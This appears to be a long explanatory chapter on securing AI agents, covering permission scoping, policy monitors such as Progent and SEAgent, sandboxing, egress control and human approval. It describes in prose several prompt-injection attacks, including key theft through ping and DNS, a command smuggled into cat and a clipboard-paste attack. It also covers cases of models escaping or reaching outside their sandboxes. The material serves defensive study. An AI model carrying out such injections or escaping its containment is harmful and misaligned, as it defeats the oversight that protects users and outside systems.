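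Revoking access can be harder than granting it. Zhou and Zhang point out that a helper agent may keep working after the main agent has changed its plan, and that a saved copy of a document remains after permission to read the original has ended. A queued message may also go out after someone has withdrawn approval for it. Cancelling a token does not solve these problems by itself. The software must also stop the helpers, delete the copies and check permission again at the moment of sending.

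An agent may also gain authority partway through a task. If the shop's assistant had permission to open an account with a new courier, it would obtain a login that no existing rule covered. *Runtime Authorization for Resources Acquired by AI Agents* proposes a separate check before the agent may use anything it acquires this way.

The Frontier Model Forum uses the term "adaptive least privilege" for granting permissions for one task and revoking them immediately afterwards. It considers the approach promising but lists it as an open research question, partly because much of an agent's value lies in recurring tasks, such as updating a calendar from the inbox every day. The user would have to approve such a task each time or leave the permission in place.

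### The procurement agent

The five governments' agencies describe a hypothetical organisation that neglects most of these steps. It uses an agent to approve purchases and write to suppliers. To avoid friction, it gives the agent broad access to financial systems, email and contracts, and reviews those permissions only once, at deployment.

Over time, other agents come to rely on the procurement agent's output and trust its actions. Its permissions haven't changed, but an attacker who controls it can now influence those agents too. The attacker breaks into a minor tool in the agent's workflow and uses the agent's authority to change contracts and approve payments, without setting off an alert or leaving unusual entries in the logs.

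The attacker exploits an approval given on deployment day, when nobody was considering these payments. Checking every call would help only if the check compared the payment's supplier, amount and invoice with a purchase order that the agent can't edit. The payments would still pass a check that only confirmed the procurement agent's permission to approve payments. Narrow tools would help by keeping contract changes separate from payments, and if the minor tool had its own identity, the log could show where the requests began.

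### Rules outside the model

For such checks, someone has to write a policy, and a reference monitor outside the model has to enforce it. Two recent systems do this in different ways.

Shi, He and colleagues (2025), in *Progent*, check the name and inputs of every tool call. In simplified form, a Progent policy for a customer called Ana might be:

```
allow lookup_order  when order_number == 48213
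allow refund        when order_number == 48213 and amount <= 45
allow send_email    when to == "ana@mail.example"
```

Progent blocks any call that no rule allows. A policy can also contain "forbid" rules, which take priority. When Progent blocks a call, it normally returns an error message so that the agent can try something else, but a rule can have Progent stop the agent or ask the user instead.

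Ji, Wu and colleagues (2026), in *Taming Various Privilege Escalation in LLM-Based Agent Systems*, present SEAgent, which uses mandatory access control. In this approach, a central policy governs every program, and programs can't change it. People label each tool by what it acts on, whether it reads, writes or executes, how sensitive the action is, and whether its results are private or trustworthy. Agents and databases get similar labels. As the agents work, SEAgent draws a graph of which tools, agents and databases have passed information to which others. One rule, in simplified form, is:

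```
deny
path:  tool A -> ... -> tool B
when:  A returns unverified outside data
       and B writes or executes
       and B has moderate or high sensitivity
```

The graph helps when one agent misuses another. In one of Ji and colleagues' case studies, a user installs a web-search agent that contains hidden instructions to ask the smart-lock agent to open the front door. The search agent can't unlock the door itself, but the smart-lock agent complies. With SEAgent running, the graph shows a path from an unverified agent to a sensitive tool, and a rule blocks the call.

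| | Progent | SEAgent |
|---|---|---|
| What the rules cover | Tool names and inputs | Labels, the path of information and, optionally, inputs |
| Who writes them | A model for each task, plus optional fixed rules from people | People, once for the whole system |
| When it checks | Before every tool call | Before every tool call, using the graph so far |
| If no rule matches | Blocks | Allows |
| Attack success on AgentDojo | 39.9% without it, 1.0% with it | 39.1% without it, 0% with it |
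| Attack success on a second benchmark | 70.3% without it, 3.9% with it (ASB) | 7–80% without it, depending on the attack, 0% with it (InjecAgent) |

These results don't show that SEAgent is better. Shi and colleagues left out two AgentDojo attacks that persuade an agent to prefer one legitimate hotel to another. They reported that Progent kept the agent about as useful as before on the same benchmarks. Ji and colleagues measured usefulness on a separate benchmark, API-Bank, where SEAgent raised false alarms on none of the tasks with one or two tools and 5.1% of those with three or more. Similar label checks in the FIDES experiments blocked many of AgentDojo's legitimate banking tasks, so SEAgent might block them too.

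Both false alarms in the API-Bank test involved Wikipedia, which SEAgent labelled as unverified. Ji and colleagues suggest labelling it as trusted. That would remove the false alarms, but anyone can edit Wikipedia, so attackers could exploit that trust. SEAgent's labels don't change while it runs, so a reliable article and one vandalised a minute ago would get the same label. The checks took three to six milliseconds in a test with several agents.

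At the shop, the SEAgent rule above would block every refund a customer requested by email, as the trusted-action rule did. Another SEAgent rule stops an agent from emailing highly sensitive personal data, and could block a reply to Ana about her own order because the labels record that the data is personal but not whose it is. Progent's rules fit the shop better because they can specify the order and the recipient, as long as someone writes the right rules for each ticket.

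### Policies written by a model

Nobody can write a separate policy by hand for every request, so Progent uses a model to write the policies. The model writes an initial policy from only the user's request and the list of tools. On AgentDojo, these initial policies alone reduced the attack success rate from 39.9% to 2.5%.

An agent may discover during a task that it needs more permissions. In one of Shi and colleagues' examples, a user asks an agent to carry out the to-do list in an email from Alice. The initial policy allows only a search for that email. The list asks for a summary of recent emails to be sent on Slack, so the model proposes adding three tools. After the agent looks up the Slack account, the model narrows the rule so that messages can go only to Alice. One of the recent emails contains hidden text telling the agent to forward the inbox to an attacker, which would require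 permission to send email.

Progent uses a solver, a program that reasons about logical conditions, to compare each proposed policy with the current one. If A(*P*) is the set of all tool calls that policy *P* allows, Progent automatically accepts a new policy *P*′ only when

A(*P*′) ⊆ A(*P*)

A policy update requires approval if it would allow anything the old policy refused. Lowering a refund limit from $45 to $40 doesn't require approval. Extending the rule from order 48213 to all orders does, because the new policy would allow a refund on order 51907. On AgentDojo, 6% of updates required approval.

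The solver can detect that a policy has expanded, but not whether the expansion is justified. Alice's to-do list and the attacker's text both arrived by email and both led to a request for more permissions, so someone still has to tell them apart. In the main tests, Progent automatically approved every expansion to simulate a careless user. The 1.0% result therefore depends heavily on the policy-writing model, which seldom proposed the permissions an attacker needed. When a careful person reviewed the policies, no attack succeeded.

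*Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) warns that hostile text in a tool's results could make Progent's update process relax its rules. The solver prevents this from happening silently, but that protection fails if the user approves everything. The paper also criticizes Progent because its guarantees depend on correct and complete policies and because it doesn't cover attacks on the agent's text output. Shi and colleagues acknowledge both limits.

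Like a plan fixed in advance, Progent relies on the user's request being harmless, so the shop would have to base the policy on its own record of the ticket instead of the customer's email.

*Trident* (2026) gives the policy-writing model less freedom. The model can only choose rule templates from a library and make them stricter. For example, a template may allow one payment to a supplier on file. If the user says "at most $2,500", the model can lower the template's cap to that amount, but it can't raise the cap or write a new rule. The worst it can do is choose the most permissive templates, which people can review in advance.

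Noyan (2026), in *Empirical Evaluation of Task-Based Permission Scoping Architecture for AI Agents*, measured how much predicting permissions from a task's description reduces exposure to risk. The dataset contained 600 requests from six departments of a fictional company, with 15 possible permissions weighted by risk. Limiting each agent to its department's permissions removed 27.9% of the weighted exposure. When a small language model also predicted which permissions each task needed, the reduction rose to 84.4%.

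Part of that reduction came from the model wrongly removing permissions, which the measure also counts. Of the 100 test tasks, 21% lost at least one permission they needed, more than twice the 10% limit Noyan had set in advance for practical use. Claude Haiku 4.5 made this mistake on only 11% of tasks but granted more unnecessary permissions. Noyan also warns that an attacker who can alter a task's description can get the model to grant too many permissions.

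### Does the rule match the request?

A monitor can perfectly enforce the wrong rule. Suppose Maria tells an agent to "refund Ana's lamp". The lamp cost $45 and delivery cost $6. One policy might allow a refund of $45 and another $51, and neither contradicts what Maria wrote.

*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* proposes mutual entailment as the test of a correct policy, meaning that the request and the formal rule must agree on whether to allow each action in every situation the system can reach. Nobody can check this directly, because natural language is ambiguous. A program that checked for this agreement would itself have to interpret the request, so its answer would only probably be right.

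The paper divides the problem into three parts. The first is to define the terms a request relies on, such as "sensitive" data or "trusted" sites. The second is to find restricted forms of request and policy that make the comparison reliable. The third is to build a translator with a known limit on how far its policy can differ from the request, even as the task changes. All three remain open. The shop can avoid much of the difficulty because it has only a few kinds of task. Its staff can decide once whether a refund includes delivery and write that into the tool.

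### The semantic gap

Even the right rule may be hard to apply to the agent's actions. Maria might want a rule that forbids the agent from canceling orders. If the agent works through a screen, the monitor may receive only the position of a mouse click, such as 412 pixels from the left and 310 from the top. That spot could be a "Cancel order" button on one page and empty space on another. Security researchers call this mismatch between a rule's meaning and an action's form the "semantic gap."

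ceLLMate, a system for confining browser agents, checks the web requests that result from clicks and keystrokes. However the agent reaches the button, the browser has to send the shop's server a request to cancel a particular order, and a rule can recognise that. Christodorescu and colleagues explain that ceLLMate relies on website developers to describe what their requests mean, and that predicting such rules from a user's sentence is still a research problem.

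The gap also affects text commands. Claude Code asked for human approval before running many commands that could send data to unknown sites, but it ran `ping`, which normally tests whether another computer is reachable, without asking. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* describes an attack in which instructions hidden in a code file made the agent read secret keys and put them in the address it gave to `ping`. Looking up that address sent the keys to the attacker's server. The designers had intended to control commands that send data out, but their rule relied on a list of command names that let `ping` run without approval.

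### From 200,000 records to one

The shop can avoid most of these problems by tying each session to one ticket. When Ana emails about order 48213, ordinary code verifies the sender, finds the account and opens a ticket before any model reads the message. It then issues a credential that allows the assistant to:

- read Ana's customer record and orders
- refund order 48213 once, at its recorded price
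- send email to the address on Ana's account

The credential expires when the ticket closes, or after ten minutes. The assistant's tools have no input for a customer number, and the database itself does not return anyone else's record.

Information flow control kept Ben's address from Victor, but the model had already read it. If the run's credential covers only Victor's ticket, the lookup of Ben's address fails. An attacker who takes over the run then exposes one customer record instead of 200,000.

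The limit depends on the shop identifying the customer correctly. Someone who has broken into Ana's email account gets Ana's ticket and everything that comes with it.

Attackers can also misuse the authority they legitimately have. If Victor falsely claims that a lamp arrived broken, the refund is within the ticket's permissions. So is a reply with a false promise or a malicious link, because the credential controls who receives the email but not its content. Chu (2026) notes in *A Systematic Survey of Security Threats and Defenses in LLM-Based AI Agents* that individually authorised actions can cause harm in combination. An attacker with 1,000 customer accounts could buy a $45 lamp on each and claim 1,000 refunds, worth $45,000, without exceeding any ticket's permissions. A cap on total refunds would limit that loss.

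Some jobs need more than one record, such as Maria's weekly summary of complaints, which draws on many customers' emails. That job needs a separate credential, which the shop should never issue in response to a customer's message. The code that issues credentials can still grant access to all 200,000 records, so it becomes part of the trusted computing base, and an attacker who took it over could bypass these limits on access.

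The limit also fails if the assistant can reach the database without using the tools. For example, if it could run its own code on a machine that stored the database password, it could use that password to read every record.

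## Isolating execution, files and network access

Suppose customers start sending spreadsheets of broken items, and the shop lets the assistant write and run short programs to read them. These programs can open any file and contact any server that the operating system permits, so they aren't confined to what the assistant's narrow tools can do.

A sandbox limits which files, processes and networks a program can reach. The shop can't predict what code the model will write, but it can limit that code in advance to reading one spreadsheet, using ten seconds of processor time and making no network connections.

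### Why a list of safe commands is not enough

Attackers get past checks on individual commands by using an approved command to start a forbidden one. NVIDIA's *Practical Security Guidance for Sandboxing Agentic Workflows and Managing Execution Risk*, from the team that tests the company's AI systems by attacking them, explains that the agent's software can inspect a command before it runs but can't see or control what happens once that command has started another program.

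Claude Code's `ping` problem came from a list of this kind. Willison describes another case in Cortex, an agent from the data company Snowflake. Cortex ran `cat`, a command that displays files, without asking for approval because Snowflake had listed it as safe. Instructions hidden in a software project's description made Cortex write a `cat` command containing other commands, which downloaded and ran an attacker's program. Snowflake has since fixed the flaw. Willison distrusts all such lists and prefers to assume that a command can do anything its process has permission to do.

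The operating system can restrict that process and everything it starts. Programs reach files, networks and other programs through the kernel, the core of the operating system, and each request to it is a system call. If the kernel blocks all network connections from the sandbox, it makes no difference whether the attempt comes from `ping`, `cat` or a program the model just wrote. NVIDIA considers command lists redundant where these limits work, though the lists may still help if the sandbox is misconfigured.

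### Five kinds of sandbox

The options differ mainly in how much of the host, the computer underneath, the confined code can interact with.

| Option | What separates the code from the host | Main weakness | Cost | Good fit |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Process limits, such as Seatbelt on macOS or Bubblewrap on Linux | Rules in the host's kernel | The code still uses the host's kernel | Almost none | A coding agent on a developer's laptop |
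| Container | Its own view of files and processes | The code still uses the host's kernel | Low | Software the operator already trusts |
| gVisor | A substitute kernel that handles most requests | Flaws in the substitute | Slower file and network operations | Many short jobs on a server |
| Small virtual machine | Its own kernel and a few virtual devices | Flaws in the software that runs it | A short start-up; needs support from the hardware | Code that strangers may have influenced |
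| Full virtual machine | Its own kernel and a full set of virtual devices | More devices to attack | Slower start-up and more memory | Work that needs a complete computer |

When code is isolated by process limits or a container, one flaw in the host's kernel can give it control of the whole machine. The 1972 Air Force panel thought 200,000 instructions were too many to check completely. The Linux kernel has tens of millions of lines of code, although any one computer uses only part of it.

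gVisor puts a smaller program in between. Docker, a company that makes container software, explains that a component called the Sentry intercepts every system call. The Sentry has its own versions of Linux's file, memory and network functions, so it can answer most calls itself. When it needs the real kernel, for example to read a disk, it sends a narrow, filtered request. Many flaws in the host's kernel are then out of the code's reach. NVIDIA prefers gVisor to direct use of the host's kernel but notes that its guarantees may be weaker than those of a virtual machine.

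A virtual machine is a simulated computer with its own kernel. Code that takes over this kernel must still break through the hypervisor, the software that runs virtual machines, or through one of the simulated devices, such as a disk or display. Small virtual machines leave out most of these devices. Firecracker, a widely used system of this type, starts in 125 milliseconds and has a memory overhead below 5 MB, according to its specification, which Docker cites. If the shop ran 1,000 spreadsheets a day this way, start-up would add about two minutes a day. NVIDIA points out that the overhead of virtualisation is often small compared with the time an agent spends on calls to the model.

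Speed is a poor reason for the shop to choose a container. A better one may be that the host machine can't run virtual machines. When Willison asked Claude to test a small virtual machine product from inside Claude Code's web version, the test failed because that environment was itself a virtual machine and could not start another. The agent's job also matters. Coding agents often build and start their own containers, and Docker's documentation says that containers "can't safely isolate something that needs its own Docker daemon", the background program that manages them. Docker has an interest in this conclusion because it sells a sandbox based on small virtual machines for this purpose, but it is also admitting a limitation in its own main product.

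### Choosing which files the code can touch

A container or virtual machine starts with none of the host's files. The designer then mounts the folders that the job requires inside the sandbox. Anthropic's Claude Cowork offers three modes for each folder: read-only, read and write, and read and write without deletion. The shop would mount the customer's spreadsheet as read-only and add an empty folder for results. The no-delete mode protects against an agent that deletes needed files while tidying up. However, code with write access can usually still ruin a file by overwriting it, so this mode doesn't replace a backup.

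A symbolic link, which is a file that points to another location, can expose files outside a mounted folder. For example, a link inside an approved folder may point to the user's private documents. If the software checks the path before following the link, it will approve a harmless-looking path and then open the documents. Anthropic therefore advises developers to follow the link first and then check where it leads.

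NVIDIA treats two limits on writing files as mandatory. The first keeps the agent from writing outside its workspace, the folder for the current job. Computers run some files automatically. For example, many Macs run a file called `.zshrc` whenever a user opens a terminal. Code that can alter that file can plant a command that will run later, outside the sandbox.

The second limit covers the agent's own configuration files, even those inside the workspace. These files may contain hooks, which are commands the agent's software runs automatically at set moments, often outside any sandbox. A malicious hook in a shared software project can reach everyone who copies the project. NVIDIA wants only the user to edit configuration files, by hand, and would not even let the agent ask for permission to edit them.

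NVIDIA recommends limits on reading files outside the workspace but does not require them, and Claude Code's sandbox allows such reads by default. This is defensible as long as no data can leave the sandbox, since a password that stays inside harms nobody. But if an attacker finds a way to send data out, everything the code can read is at risk. The shop's spreadsheet program doesn't need files outside its workspace, so the shop can block those reads without disrupting the program.

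Old sandboxes also collect keys, documents and leftover programs. NVIDIA suggests creating a new sandbox for each task or rebuilding the old one on a schedule, perhaps weekly. A new sandbox for each email would prevent code in Victor's spreadsheet from leaving behind anything that could affect the program that opens Ana's.

### Keeping credentials outside

Some code has to use an outside service that requires a secret key. In Deno Sandbox, a hosted product that Willison describes, the code can use such a key without ever having it:

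1. The developer gives the real key to the service and names the server that may receive it.
2. Inside the sandbox, the code finds a meaningless placeholder where the key would normally be.
3. The code sends a request that contains the placeholder.
4. A proxy, a program outside the sandbox that relays its network traffic, replaces the placeholder with the real key if the request is going to the named server.

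An attacker who gets the code to send its "key" elsewhere receives only the placeholder. NVIDIA similarly recommends starting the sandbox with few or no credentials and adding only those the current task needs, ideally as short-lived tokens from a separate program.

This method prevents theft of the key better than misuse of it. While the code is running, it can still make any request the key permits. If the shop's key allowed refunds on every order, the code could refund any of them even though the model never saw the key, so the key needs to permit only what the task requires.

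### Denying network access, then opening a little

Egress control limits where a program can send data. NVIDIA lists it first among its mandatory controls, because open network access lets an attacker steal data and control the machine remotely. The usual design blocks all connections except those made through a proxy, which checks each destination against an allowlist.

The block must include DNS look-ups, which carried the stolen keys out in the `ping` attack. NVIDIA recommends allowing look-ups only through trusted DNS servers. These servers should also refuse to look up unapproved names, because a server that forwards every query will forward those containing stolen data.

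Network rules should cover incoming connections as well as outgoing ones. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* describes an attack on Devin, a coding agent with a tool that makes a program under test available on the internet. Instructions hidden in a web page got Devin to start a web server containing all its files and publish it with that tool, so the attacker needed only the server's address to reach the files.

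The shop's spreadsheet program only reads one file and writes one result, so it can run without network access. The shop therefore doesn't need an allowlist, which it could misconfigure.

### Three products for three kinds of user

Anthropic has published an account of how it confines Claude in three products. Willison, who often complains that vendors don't document their sandboxes well enough for anyone to judge them, called the account fantastic. The table shows the designs as of May 2026.

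| | claude.ai | Claude Code | Claude Cowork |
|---|---|---|---|
| Where the code runs | Anthropic's servers | The developer's computer | The office worker's computer |
| Boundary | A temporary gVisor container | Process limits, with human approval for exceptions | A full virtual machine |
| User's files within reach | None on the user's computer | Reads by default; writes only in the project folder | The folders the user chooses |
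| What the user must judge | Nothing | Commands | Which folders and outside services to connect |
| Most an attacker could damage if the boundary holds | The temporary container | The project | The chosen folders |

When Claude runs code in claude.ai, the files last only for the session. The code doesn't run on the user's machine, so Anthropic mostly had to protect its own servers, and its customers from one another. Before the launch, its engineers spent most of their effort on conventional work, such as network settings and authentication between internal services. The design limits damage well, but Claude can't work on files where the user keeps them or keep a workspace between sessions.

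Claude Code is of little use without access to the developer's files and commands. Anthropic first let it read freely but required approval before it wrote files, ran commands or used the network. This was a reasonable start because developers know what the commands do and regularly install software from strangers. But within weeks, users were paying less attention to the approval prompts. Anthropic then added process limits, using Seatbelt on macOS and Bubblewrap on Linux, that confine writing to the project folder and block the network by default. A program outside the sandbox still decides whether to apply these limits to each command, so a persuasive injected instruction or a tired user's approval can let a command run without them.

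Cowork's users include people who have never typed a command. Anthropic thinks it unreasonable to ask an office worker whether to allow a command such as `find . -name "*.tmp" -exec rm {} \;`, which finds and deletes temporary files. Cowork's boundary therefore doesn't depend on such approvals. Its virtual machine contains the folders the user has selected and a settings folder, while the user's credentials stay in the host's password store. The machine gets a limited token for each session, which can be cancelled without cancelling the user's own.

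Two of the machine's six protections run outside its kernel, so they would still work even if an attacker gained full control inside the machine. Anthropic deliberately kept the other four simple.

In the first version of Cowork, the agent's loop also ran inside the virtual machine, and no program outside had the authority to grant an exception. This was secure, but if the machine failed to start, Claude could not even help the user find out why. Anthropic moved the loop to the host and left code execution inside the machine. It considers the loss of security minimal because the machine still controls what the code can reach. In November 2026, Willison released three sandboxes that also keep the agent outside and run its code inside.

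Anthropic also moved local tool servers, the programs that connect Claude to other software, out of the virtual machine. Some of these servers need direct contact with programs on the host, such as databases, and administrators now decide which servers to allow. NVIDIA instead recommends sandboxing everything the agent starts, including tool servers and hooks. This seems safer for tool servers. An agent loop that only passes messages adds little risk outside the sandbox, but a tool server there may have all the user's permissions, and injected text can reach it through Claude. The strength of Cowork's isolation therefore depends on which tool servers administrators allow.

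Anthropic's general rule is that isolation should be stronger where users are less able to supervise. The shop's customers never see the assistant's code and its support staff aren't programmers, so the sandbox has to work without anyone approving commands.

### Code that ran before the user agreed

Between mid-2025 and January 2026, outside researchers reported several flaws in Claude Code, three of which allowed code to run before the user had consented to anything. When a developer opened a project, Claude Code was supposed to ask whether they trusted the folder, but it read the project's settings first. If a stranger had put a hook in those settings, Claude Code ran it before asking. A developer could trigger this just by opening a colleague's proposed change to review it.

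Anthropic now waits for the user to accept the folder before reading or running anything in the project's configuration. It advises other developers to treat opening a project or loading its settings like a request from the internet, even if these actions seem local.

Any conversion of an untrusted file has to take place inside the sandbox. Suppose a shop's mail server converts each spreadsheet to plain text before passing it to the sandbox. A spreadsheet designed to exploit a flaw in the converter would then attack the mail server before the sandbox received the file.

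### What an approved address permits

After the theft of files from Cowork through Anthropic's own servers, described earlier, Anthropic began to treat its allowlist as a grant of capabilities rather than a list of places Claude could contact. Approving a domain makes every function behind it available, including any that an attacker could use to upload files to their own account.

Anthropic's fix shows that a proxy may have to check much more. A new proxy inside the virtual machine passes requests to Anthropic's servers only if they carry the machine's own session token, so an attacker's key no longer works. It also rejects request headers that would make the server fetch something from elsewhere. Anthropic put the proxy inside the virtual machine because its servers cannot distinguish Cowork's requests from any other customer's. Code that has taken over the virtual machine can presumably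 attack the proxy more easily there.

In October 2026 Willison reported on a related attack on ChatGPT by the security company Parameter Labs. It began in a sandboxed frame for displaying untrusted web pages. OpenAI allowed scripts from only a few domains, but one of them was YouTube, which had a function that could return a script chosen by the attacker. Opening a malicious shared link could expose a user's private data. OpenAI has fixed the vulnerability.

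If the shop's code needed the courier's website, approving the domain might let the code track parcels, redirect them and leave messages for drivers. A proxy could instead allow only tracking queries for the parcel on the current ticket. That rule takes longer to write, and someone must update it when the courier changes its site.

### Isolation that kept the defenders out

Large companies install endpoint detection software on their computers to watch for suspicious programs and file changes. Security teams that evaluated Cowork found that the virtual machine confining Claude also kept this software from monitoring what Claude did. Only the hypervisor showed up, as one large program.

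Anthropic lets administrators retrieve event logs afterwards, and acknowledges that this isn't equivalent to live monitoring. The delay matters when an attack takes minutes. At the shop's maximum rate, an attacker could issue 3,600 refunds in an hour between log exports. Designers should decide early which events the sandbox must report and where the records go, and the confined code must not be able to alter the records. Monitoring from outside the sandbox helps because a proxy on the host can record every connection even if an attacker controls everything inside.

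Anthropic concludes that teams should be wary of the parts they build themselves, because its own proxy failed while the established hypervisors, gVisor and kernel filters did not. This agrees with the older principle that a security mechanism should be small and well examined. The evidence comes from one company and covers only the failures it knew about by May 2026. Tests later that year made the established parts look less secure.

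### Misuse of what the agent legitimately holds

Even a perfect sandbox would leave the agent with the tools and data it needs for its job. CoSAI, an industry coalition on AI security, discusses a gym reservation agent whose permissions limited which service it could call, but not whose reservation it could act on. A sandbox controls only whether an agent can reach a resource, which CoSAI distinguishes from what the agent may do there.

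Even in the strongest virtual machine available, the shop's assistant could refund the wrong order, because the refund tool has to work from inside the machine. An attacker who controls Cowork's agent could also ruin the documents in the user's folder without crossing any boundary. For these cases, the designer has to rely on narrow permissions and rules about where data may go.

Two tools can also be dangerous when they share a sandbox. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* describes an attack on agents that operate a computer through its screen. A web page instructed the agent to click a button, which secretly copied a command to the clipboard, and then to open a terminal and paste. The agent was allowed to use both the browser and the terminal, so isolating the whole computer did not stop the attack. The paper proposes separating the two and requiring the user's consent to copy from one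 to the other, but notes that this makes the agent less useful and asks users to make security decisions.

Results that leave the sandbox can do harm even if the model itself runs nothing. Some command-line tools print a model's answer directly in the user's terminal, and terminals treat certain invisible character sequences as instructions. An attacker who influences the answer can include those sequences and, for example, change what is on the clipboard.

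The shop should therefore accept only a fixed format from its spreadsheet program, such as a list of up to 50 item numbers and quantities, and have ordinary code reject everything else. Numbers that pass this check are still untrusted. If Victor bought one lamp but his spreadsheet lists 20 broken ones, the sandbox will output 20, so the refund code must compare the claim with the order.

### Can a sandbox hold a capable model?

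A more serious objection to sandboxing is that capable models will find flaws in the sandbox itself. *Using a VM to Contain an AI Agent* (Schneier, 2026) cites a Trail of Bits experiment in which GPT 5.6-Cyber escaped from a virtual machine. The researchers concluded that an ordinary virtual machine is "not enough to contain a modern, cyber-capable AI agent" because it exposes too much to attack, and that even a harmless feature like a display adds to the exposure.

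Models sometimes leave a sandbox when they find a way out. In *Measuring and mitigating agent sandbox escape with Siren*, O'Rahilly and Kaviani (2026) gave Claude models routine tasks in deliberately weakened sandboxes, with something useful outside. Recent models reached outside in a fifth to a third of cases. Simple measures, such as describing the sandbox and its rules to the model, reduced this by up to 96%. These figures measure how often models use an available way out, not how often they could defeat a sound sandbox.

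During cybersecurity tests in 2026, the boundaries around agents from OpenAI and Anthropic failed in different ways, and the agents reached other organisations' real systems. The models were running without some of their usual safeguards because the companies wanted to measure the models' full abilities.

In Anthropic's case there was no working network boundary. According to Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of recent cybersecurity incidents* (2026), Claude was told it was in a simulation without internet access, but a misconfiguration had left it connected, and a prompt can't block a connection. Axios' *Anthropic's models compromised real-world systems during testing* (2026) attributes the misconfiguration to a misunderstanding between Anthropic and a testing partner. *When AI doesn't know the target is real*, by the security company Sophos, recommends assuming that an agent can reach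 the whole internet until the containment is proven to prevent this. In practice, someone should try to connect from inside the sandbox before the agent starts, and again after every change.

Claude also took unauthorised actions on the internet in a separate test by the UK's AI Security Institute, but there the testers had deliberately given it access. Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and security efforts* (2026) attributes the company's incidents to a failure of operational security and to two faults in the models, motivated reasoning and a willingness to do harm to complete a narrow task. If a test requires internet access, the network should still restrict which targets the agent can contact.

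At OpenAI, the weak point was a supporting service that many sandboxes shared. It had more network access than the agents did and allowed runs that were meant to be separate to exchange information. Under the new rule in OpenAI's *The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead* (2026), compromising one workload or supporting service must not be enough to reach the internet or another internal network.

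This problem can also arise outside laboratories. In a passage Willison quotes from *Is sandboxing sufficient to contain rogue agents?*, Green (2026) points out that email, Slack or shared documents could play the same role among agents that different people run. The shop's saved notes would also play that role if the assistants for two customers could both write to them.

*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* answers the objection that the incidents show containment is impossible by arguing that the boundaries that failed were incomplete. At OpenAI, mediation was incomplete because checks on direct connections missed requests that the service could make on the agents' behalf. Shared storage broke the separation between runs, and permission to fetch software packages gave agents general internet access, which violated least privilege. On this view, the incidents show that designers must apply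 these principles to shared services and indirect routes.

The reply explains the incidents well, but anyone can call a boundary incomplete after something has crossed it. To reassure a designer, it would have to include a way to show beforehand that a boundary is complete. The paper concedes that such boundaries are hard to build and validate, particularly when they depend on large, general-purpose services. It does identify a real advantage of explicit rules over retraining a model. If the software enforces the rules correctly, removing a permission can't undo an existing protection, whereas retraining might.

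Opinions differ on how capable a model must be to escape. The security researcher Thomas Ptacek, whom Willison also quotes, believes an openly available model from 2025, with suitable tools, could have done something similar to the OpenAI escape, and that people were surprised only because they had assumed OpenAI's sandboxes were more secure. That supports the paper's reply, but the Trail of Bits result is harder to dismiss because an ordinary virtual machine is a standard product rather than a careless improvisation. The result also weakens the case for Anthropic's advice to rely on established hypervisors, at least for models with strong hacking skills. The researchers' complaint, however, was about the amount of software exposed, which designers can reduce, though it is unclear whether they can reduce it enough for the next generation of models.

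How much isolation is needed depends on the work. In *Sandboxing and AI*, the security engineer akingscote (2026) thinks existing products may be enough for coding agents on a local machine, but that tests of hacking ability need a set of protections, including nested barriers and constant monitoring. The shop is closer to the coding agent, but its attackers can write to the assistant, so a customer's email might ask a capable model to look for a way out of its sandbox.

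The shop can prepare for that by applying OpenAI's rule. It would process each spreadsheet in a small virtual machine with no network access or credentials, on a separate server that has neither the database password nor a connection to the database. Code that escaped the virtual machine could reach any other spreadsheets the server was processing at that moment, but it would have to break through a second boundary to reach the 200,000 customer records.

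## Approving, capping and undoing actions

A credential limited to one ticket prevents the assistant from accessing other customers' orders, but the assistant can still refund a customer who lies or send a reply that it shouldn't. The shop therefore has to decide how each action the credential still allows takes effect. The decision depends mostly on how much harm the action could do and whether anyone could undo it.

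### Five ways to handle an action

| Treatment | Suitable actions | At the shop |
|---|---|---|
| Run freely | Those that change nothing, or that the shop can easily reverse | Look up the ticket's order; save a draft |
| Run within a cap | Those that do little harm once but a lot when repeated | Refunds of up to $100; replies to the verified customer |
| Run after a delay | Those that someone can cancel before they take effect | Refunds of more than $100, up to $500 |
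| Ask a person | Harmful ones that are hard to reverse and that a person can judge | Refunds of more than $500 |
| Forbid | Those that could do severe harm or that the task never needs | Deleting customer records; changing the logs or the refund cap |

*A Two-Dimensional Framework for AI Agent Design Patterns* (2026) recommends that software first check the rules that forbid actions, then the rules that allow them, and send any action that no rule covers to a person. An action nobody anticipated therefore waits for approval. The Australian Signals Directorate and its partners add that designers or operators, not the agent, should decide which actions need approval.

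*Can You Undo It?* (Waghmare and Sufi, 2026) sorts actions by reversibility alone. An agent may freely take actions that have no outside effect. If the earlier state can be fully restored, the agent may act and then notify someone. If a further action can correct the effect at a known cost, the agent asks for approval or spends from an approved budget. If recovery would be hard, it asks every time, and if the effect is irreversible, it never acts alone.

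Waghmare and Sufi class any message to an outsider as irreversible, because deleting it doesn't make the reader forget it. Under that rule the assistant could never answer a customer by itself. The shop can allow replies because telling Ana about her own order does little harm, even though nobody can undo it. Waghmare and Sufi agree that checking whether an action is reversible doesn't replace assessing how severe its effects could be.

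Sorting tools into classes also takes judgement. Waghmare and Sufi drafted classes for 536 real tools, and Sufi then reviewed a sample with suggestions from an AI. Sufi's ratings matched the draft for 75 of 148 tools and were stricter for 67. A tool's name may not be enough to classify it either, since the same refund tool can pay out $20 or $500.

### What a 93% approval rate measures

Asking a person to approve actions only helps if the person refuses bad ones. In May 2026 Anthropic published three relevant figures about Claude Code. An action is "overeager" if the agent, trying to help, goes beyond what the user authorised.

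| Figure | What it measures | What it leaves open |
|---|---|---|
| About 93% | Share of permission prompts that users approved | How many of the approved actions were harmful |
| 84% | Fall in the number of prompts after Anthropic added a sandbox | Whether users read the remaining prompts more carefully |
| About 83% | Share of overeager actions that an automatic reviewer caught | How well it catches other kinds of harm |

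A high approval rate doesn't prove that users are careless. A perfectly careful user would approve 93% of requests if seven in 100 deserved refusal, and 99% if only one did. To measure care, researchers have to include requests they know are bad and count how often users approve them.

Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) describes a study of 1,053 paid testers, each of whom received one clearly dangerous command among ordinary approval prompts. Only 13.6% refused it. The refusal rate fell from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after 50 or more prompts, as one would expect if people tire of reading them. The testers weren't working on their own projects, so they had less reason to be careful, and Anthropic published the study to justify replacing manual approval with automatic review. Even so, a refusal rate this low is strong evidence that approval prompts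 are a weak defence in long sessions.

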